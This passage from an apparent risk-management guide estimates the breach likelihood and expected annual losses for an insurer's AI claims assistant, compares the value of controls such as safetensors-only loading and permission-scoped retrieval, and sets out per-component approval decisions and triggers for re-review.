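Verizon has far more cases, but its sample isn't random either. Publicly disclosed breaches are more likely to enter it, and ransomware may be overrepresented. In its data-loss records, staff use of unapproved AI services was the third most common non-malicious insider action, and source code was what staff submitted most often. Verizon's main AI findings don't cover attacks on companies' own models. Outside companies played a part in 48% of all breaches. According to Verizon's *2026 Data Breach Investigations Report Executive Summary* (2026), the share in finance and insurance was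 34%. These figures cover every kind of supplier, so they don't measure the risk from reused models.

Neither report can give the chance that a company will have a breach. Every organisation in IBM's survey had already had one. To estimate the chance of an AI-related breach, the insurer would have to multiply the 21% by its own chance of having any breach that year. The result would be 0.42% if that chance were 2%, and 4.2% if it were 20%. The 13% that the Australian Signals Directorate quotes probably comes from the 2025 edition, in which case it also covers only organisations that had already had a breach.

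### Whether a review's answers predict breaches

Reviewers ask suppliers about their controls because they expect the answers to help predict future breaches. IBM's figures allow a rough test of this for one common question, whether a company controls access to its AI.

Of the organisations with an AI-related breach, 92% lacked proper AI access controls. That sounds decisive, but the controls might be just as rare elsewhere. IBM also reports that 40% of organisations used access controls on AI models and data. If this refers to all 602, the numbers work out roughly as follows:

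| | Organisations | With an AI-related breach | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| With access controls | 241 | 10 | 4% |
| Without access controls | 361 | 116 | 32% |

Organisations without controls were about eight times as likely to report that their breach involved AI. The real effect may be much smaller, because IBM may have asked the two questions differently and people who have just had an AI-related breach are more likely to call their earlier controls inadequate. All 602 organisations had a breach, so the comparison leaves out those that avoided one. IBM sells security products and paid for the research.

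IBM also found in 2025 that breaches cost about $192,000 less at organisations with AI governance technology and $147,000 less at those with governance policies. These figures cover only breaches that happened, so they don't show that governance prevents them.

A proper test of a questionnaire, certificate or outside security rating would record each organisation's result first, then count its later breaches. The insurer couldn't learn much from its own suppliers. If it had 200 and 2% had a breach each year, it would see about four breaches a year. Even if the poorly rated half had twice the risk of the other half, the insurer would expect about three breaches in the first group and one in the second, a difference that could easily be chance. Anyone selling a rating should be able to say how many organisations they followed, whether they rated them before the breaches, how large the difference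 was, and who paid for the study.

Evidence about ordinary companies would apply to some AI risks better than others. Outside ratings rely on what is visible from the internet, so they could detect a model server without a login, but not a backdoored adapter or a bad line in a copied prompt. Given the causes IBM found, a supplier with good general security is probably better at protecting its AI applications, but there is less reason to think it checks the weights it downloads.

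Verizon advises companies to compare their own controls with those typical of their industry and adjust their estimates up or down. The size of the adjustment is still a judgement, and the insurer should record it as one.

### Expected loss from the claims assistant

Expected loss is the chance of a harm in a year multiplied by its cost. The example below rates the claims assistant as it was before the review, when engineers opened a pickle adapter on the main server and one service account could read all 200,000 documents. Every chance, effect and control cost is an assumption. The assumed $6 million cost of a large breach is close to IBM's 2026 average of $6.3 million for financial services.

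| Risk | Chance in a year | Cost | Expected loss before | After three controls |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Code in a model file runs on the server and steals data | 0.2% | $6 million | $12,000 | $1,200 |
| A hidden instruction in a document gets customers' data out | 0.5% | $6 million | $30,000 | $15,000 |
| Staff see files they shouldn't, and the insurer has to investigate | 25% | $80,000 | $20,000 | $2,000 |
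| A backdoored adapter distorts summaries | 0.2% | $500,000 | $1,000 | $1,000 |
| Total | | | $63,000 | $19,200 |

The matrix at the start of this section would colour all four risks green, although the largest is 30 times the smallest.

The first chance assumes that the team tries ten outside model files a year and that 1 in 5,000 such files is malicious. Ali and Case's scans of Hugging Face suggest a rate between about 1 in 2,600 and 1 in 82,000, depending on what counts as malicious. The chances of prompt injection and a backdoor have no similar basis.

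The three controls are assumed to work as follows:

- **Safetensors only** prevents 75% of the harm from code in model files. Attackers can still use scripts published with a model.
- **Isolated loading** prevents 60% of what remains. Some code stays inactive until the model is in regular use.
- **Retrieval under the user's own permissions** prevents 90% of the unauthorised viewing. It also halves the cost of a successful prompt injection, because a handler can open about 20,000 documents instead of 200,000. The cost doesn't fall by 90% because the insurer would still need lawyers and investigators.

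Adding the controls in this order lowers the total from $63,000 to $54,000, then to $52,200, then to $19,200. Isolated loading seems to add little because the safetensors rule has already removed most of the same risk. Without that rule, isolated loading would save the insurer $7,200 a year instead of $1,800.

The next table shows how much each control would save in a year as the least certain numbers vary. The assumed annual costs are in the headings.

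| Assumption | Safetensors only ($2,000) | Isolated loading as well ($5,000) | User's own permissions ($15,000) |
|---|---|---|---|
| As above | $9,000 | $1,800 | $33,000 |
| Malicious files ten times rarer | $900 | $180 | $33,000 |
| Malicious files ten times more common | $90,000 | $18,000 | $33,000 |
| Theft by prompt injection ten times rarer | $9,000 | $1,800 | $19,500 |
| Unauthorised viewing ten times rarer | $9,000 | $1,800 | $16,800 |
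| Both of these ten times rarer | $9,000 | $1,800 | $3,300 |
| Large breach costs $12 million | $18,000 | $3,600 | $48,000 |

Running retrieval under the user's permissions is the safest investment. It reduces two risks and is still worthwhile if either one is ten times rarer than assumed, but not if both are. The safetensors rule pays for itself unless the chance of a harmful file running is below about 0.04% a year.

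Isolated loading is harder to justify for this application alone. But if five similar applications shared the isolated machine, each application's share of the cost would be $1,000 a year, and the savings would be $1,800. The insurer might also want isolated loading as protection against a rare, large loss. Malicious model files would cost it nothing in almost every year, but might cost $6 million in one year. A company that would struggle to survive such a loss can reasonably pay more than the average yearly loss to avoid it.

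The calculation also leaves out malicious packages such as the LiteLLM versions of March 2026, and 200,000 documents could hold more customers' records than the breaches in IBM's survey exposed. The insurer can use the estimate to rank the controls, but it shouldn't put $63,000 in its budget as a forecast.

### Accept, restrict, replace or reject

The manager can make a separate decision for each part, so a problem with one of them needn't stop the whole project.

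| Part | Decision | Condition or reason |
|---|---|---|
| Language model | Accept | Only the verified revision, compressed and signed by the insurer |
| Retrieval model | Restrict | Separate process without internet access |
| Document search | Restrict | Each handler's own permissions apply |
| Adapter from account B | Replace | The insurer trains one on summaries its own staff wrote |
| Letter-writing tool | Reject for now | The team can apply again after testing the limits on addresses and data |

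Suppose replacing the adapter costs $5,000 a year, spread over the replacement's useful life. Preventing a $500,000 loss from a backdoor would justify that only if the chance of the loss were at least 1% a year, five times the assumed figure. The true chance could be above or below 1%, so the expected loss alone doesn't settle what to do. However, the missing licence and parent version are good reasons to replace the adapter even if its weights are harmless.

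Accepting a risk should be a recorded decision by someone with the authority to pay for the consequences. The record should state the exact revisions, the remaining risks, the assumptions behind the rating, the level of evidence and the date of the next review. The level of evidence for a backdoor is only "demonstrated", which justifies using a wide range for its probability, but not entering zero.

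Rejecting a part also carries risk. If the claims team loses the assistant, some handlers may paste letters into a public chatbot instead. Baker Donelson reports that 43% of organisations in IBM's 2026 survey had an incident involving shadow AI, up from 20% a year earlier. The insurer can lower that risk by offering staff a restricted version while engineers fix the rest.

### When to review again

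Most changes to an approved system need only part of the review again.

| Event | What to repeat |
|---|---|
| New model version or adapter | Trace, scan and load it in isolation, then test the model and adapter together |
| Changed system prompt or chat template | Read every difference and rerun the fixed set of tests |
| New data source | Find out who can add text to it and who may read it; test for prompt injection |
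| New tool | Try the worst requests the model could make |
| New group of users | Look for secrets in the prompt and check document permissions |
| New library or package version | Check for known flaws and changed default settings |
| Alert about a model, or a breach at a supplier or hub | Search by hash and find out whether any application loaded the affected files |
| Publisher sells or deletes its account | Confirm who now controls the name |
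| Planned review date | Compare the running system with the approved record |

The insurer shouldn't rely on people to report every change. The hash check that runs on the prompt at startup can also cover the models, template and list of tools, and stop the assistant if any of them has changed. The check won't detect a new group of users or a change in who can add documents, so the assistant's owner still has to watch for those.

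Each event also needs a deadline and someone responsible for meeting it. Verizon found that organisations took a median of 43 days to fully fix flaws that attackers were known to exploit, up from 32 days the year before. In 2025 they fully fixed only 26% of such flaws.

A new tool can change the rating substantially. Suppose giving the claims team its letter-writing tool raises the chance of theft by prompt injection from 0.5% to 2% a year, even with all three controls in place. The expected annual loss from that risk would rise from $15,000 to $60,000, nearly as much as the expected loss from the whole assistant before the review.
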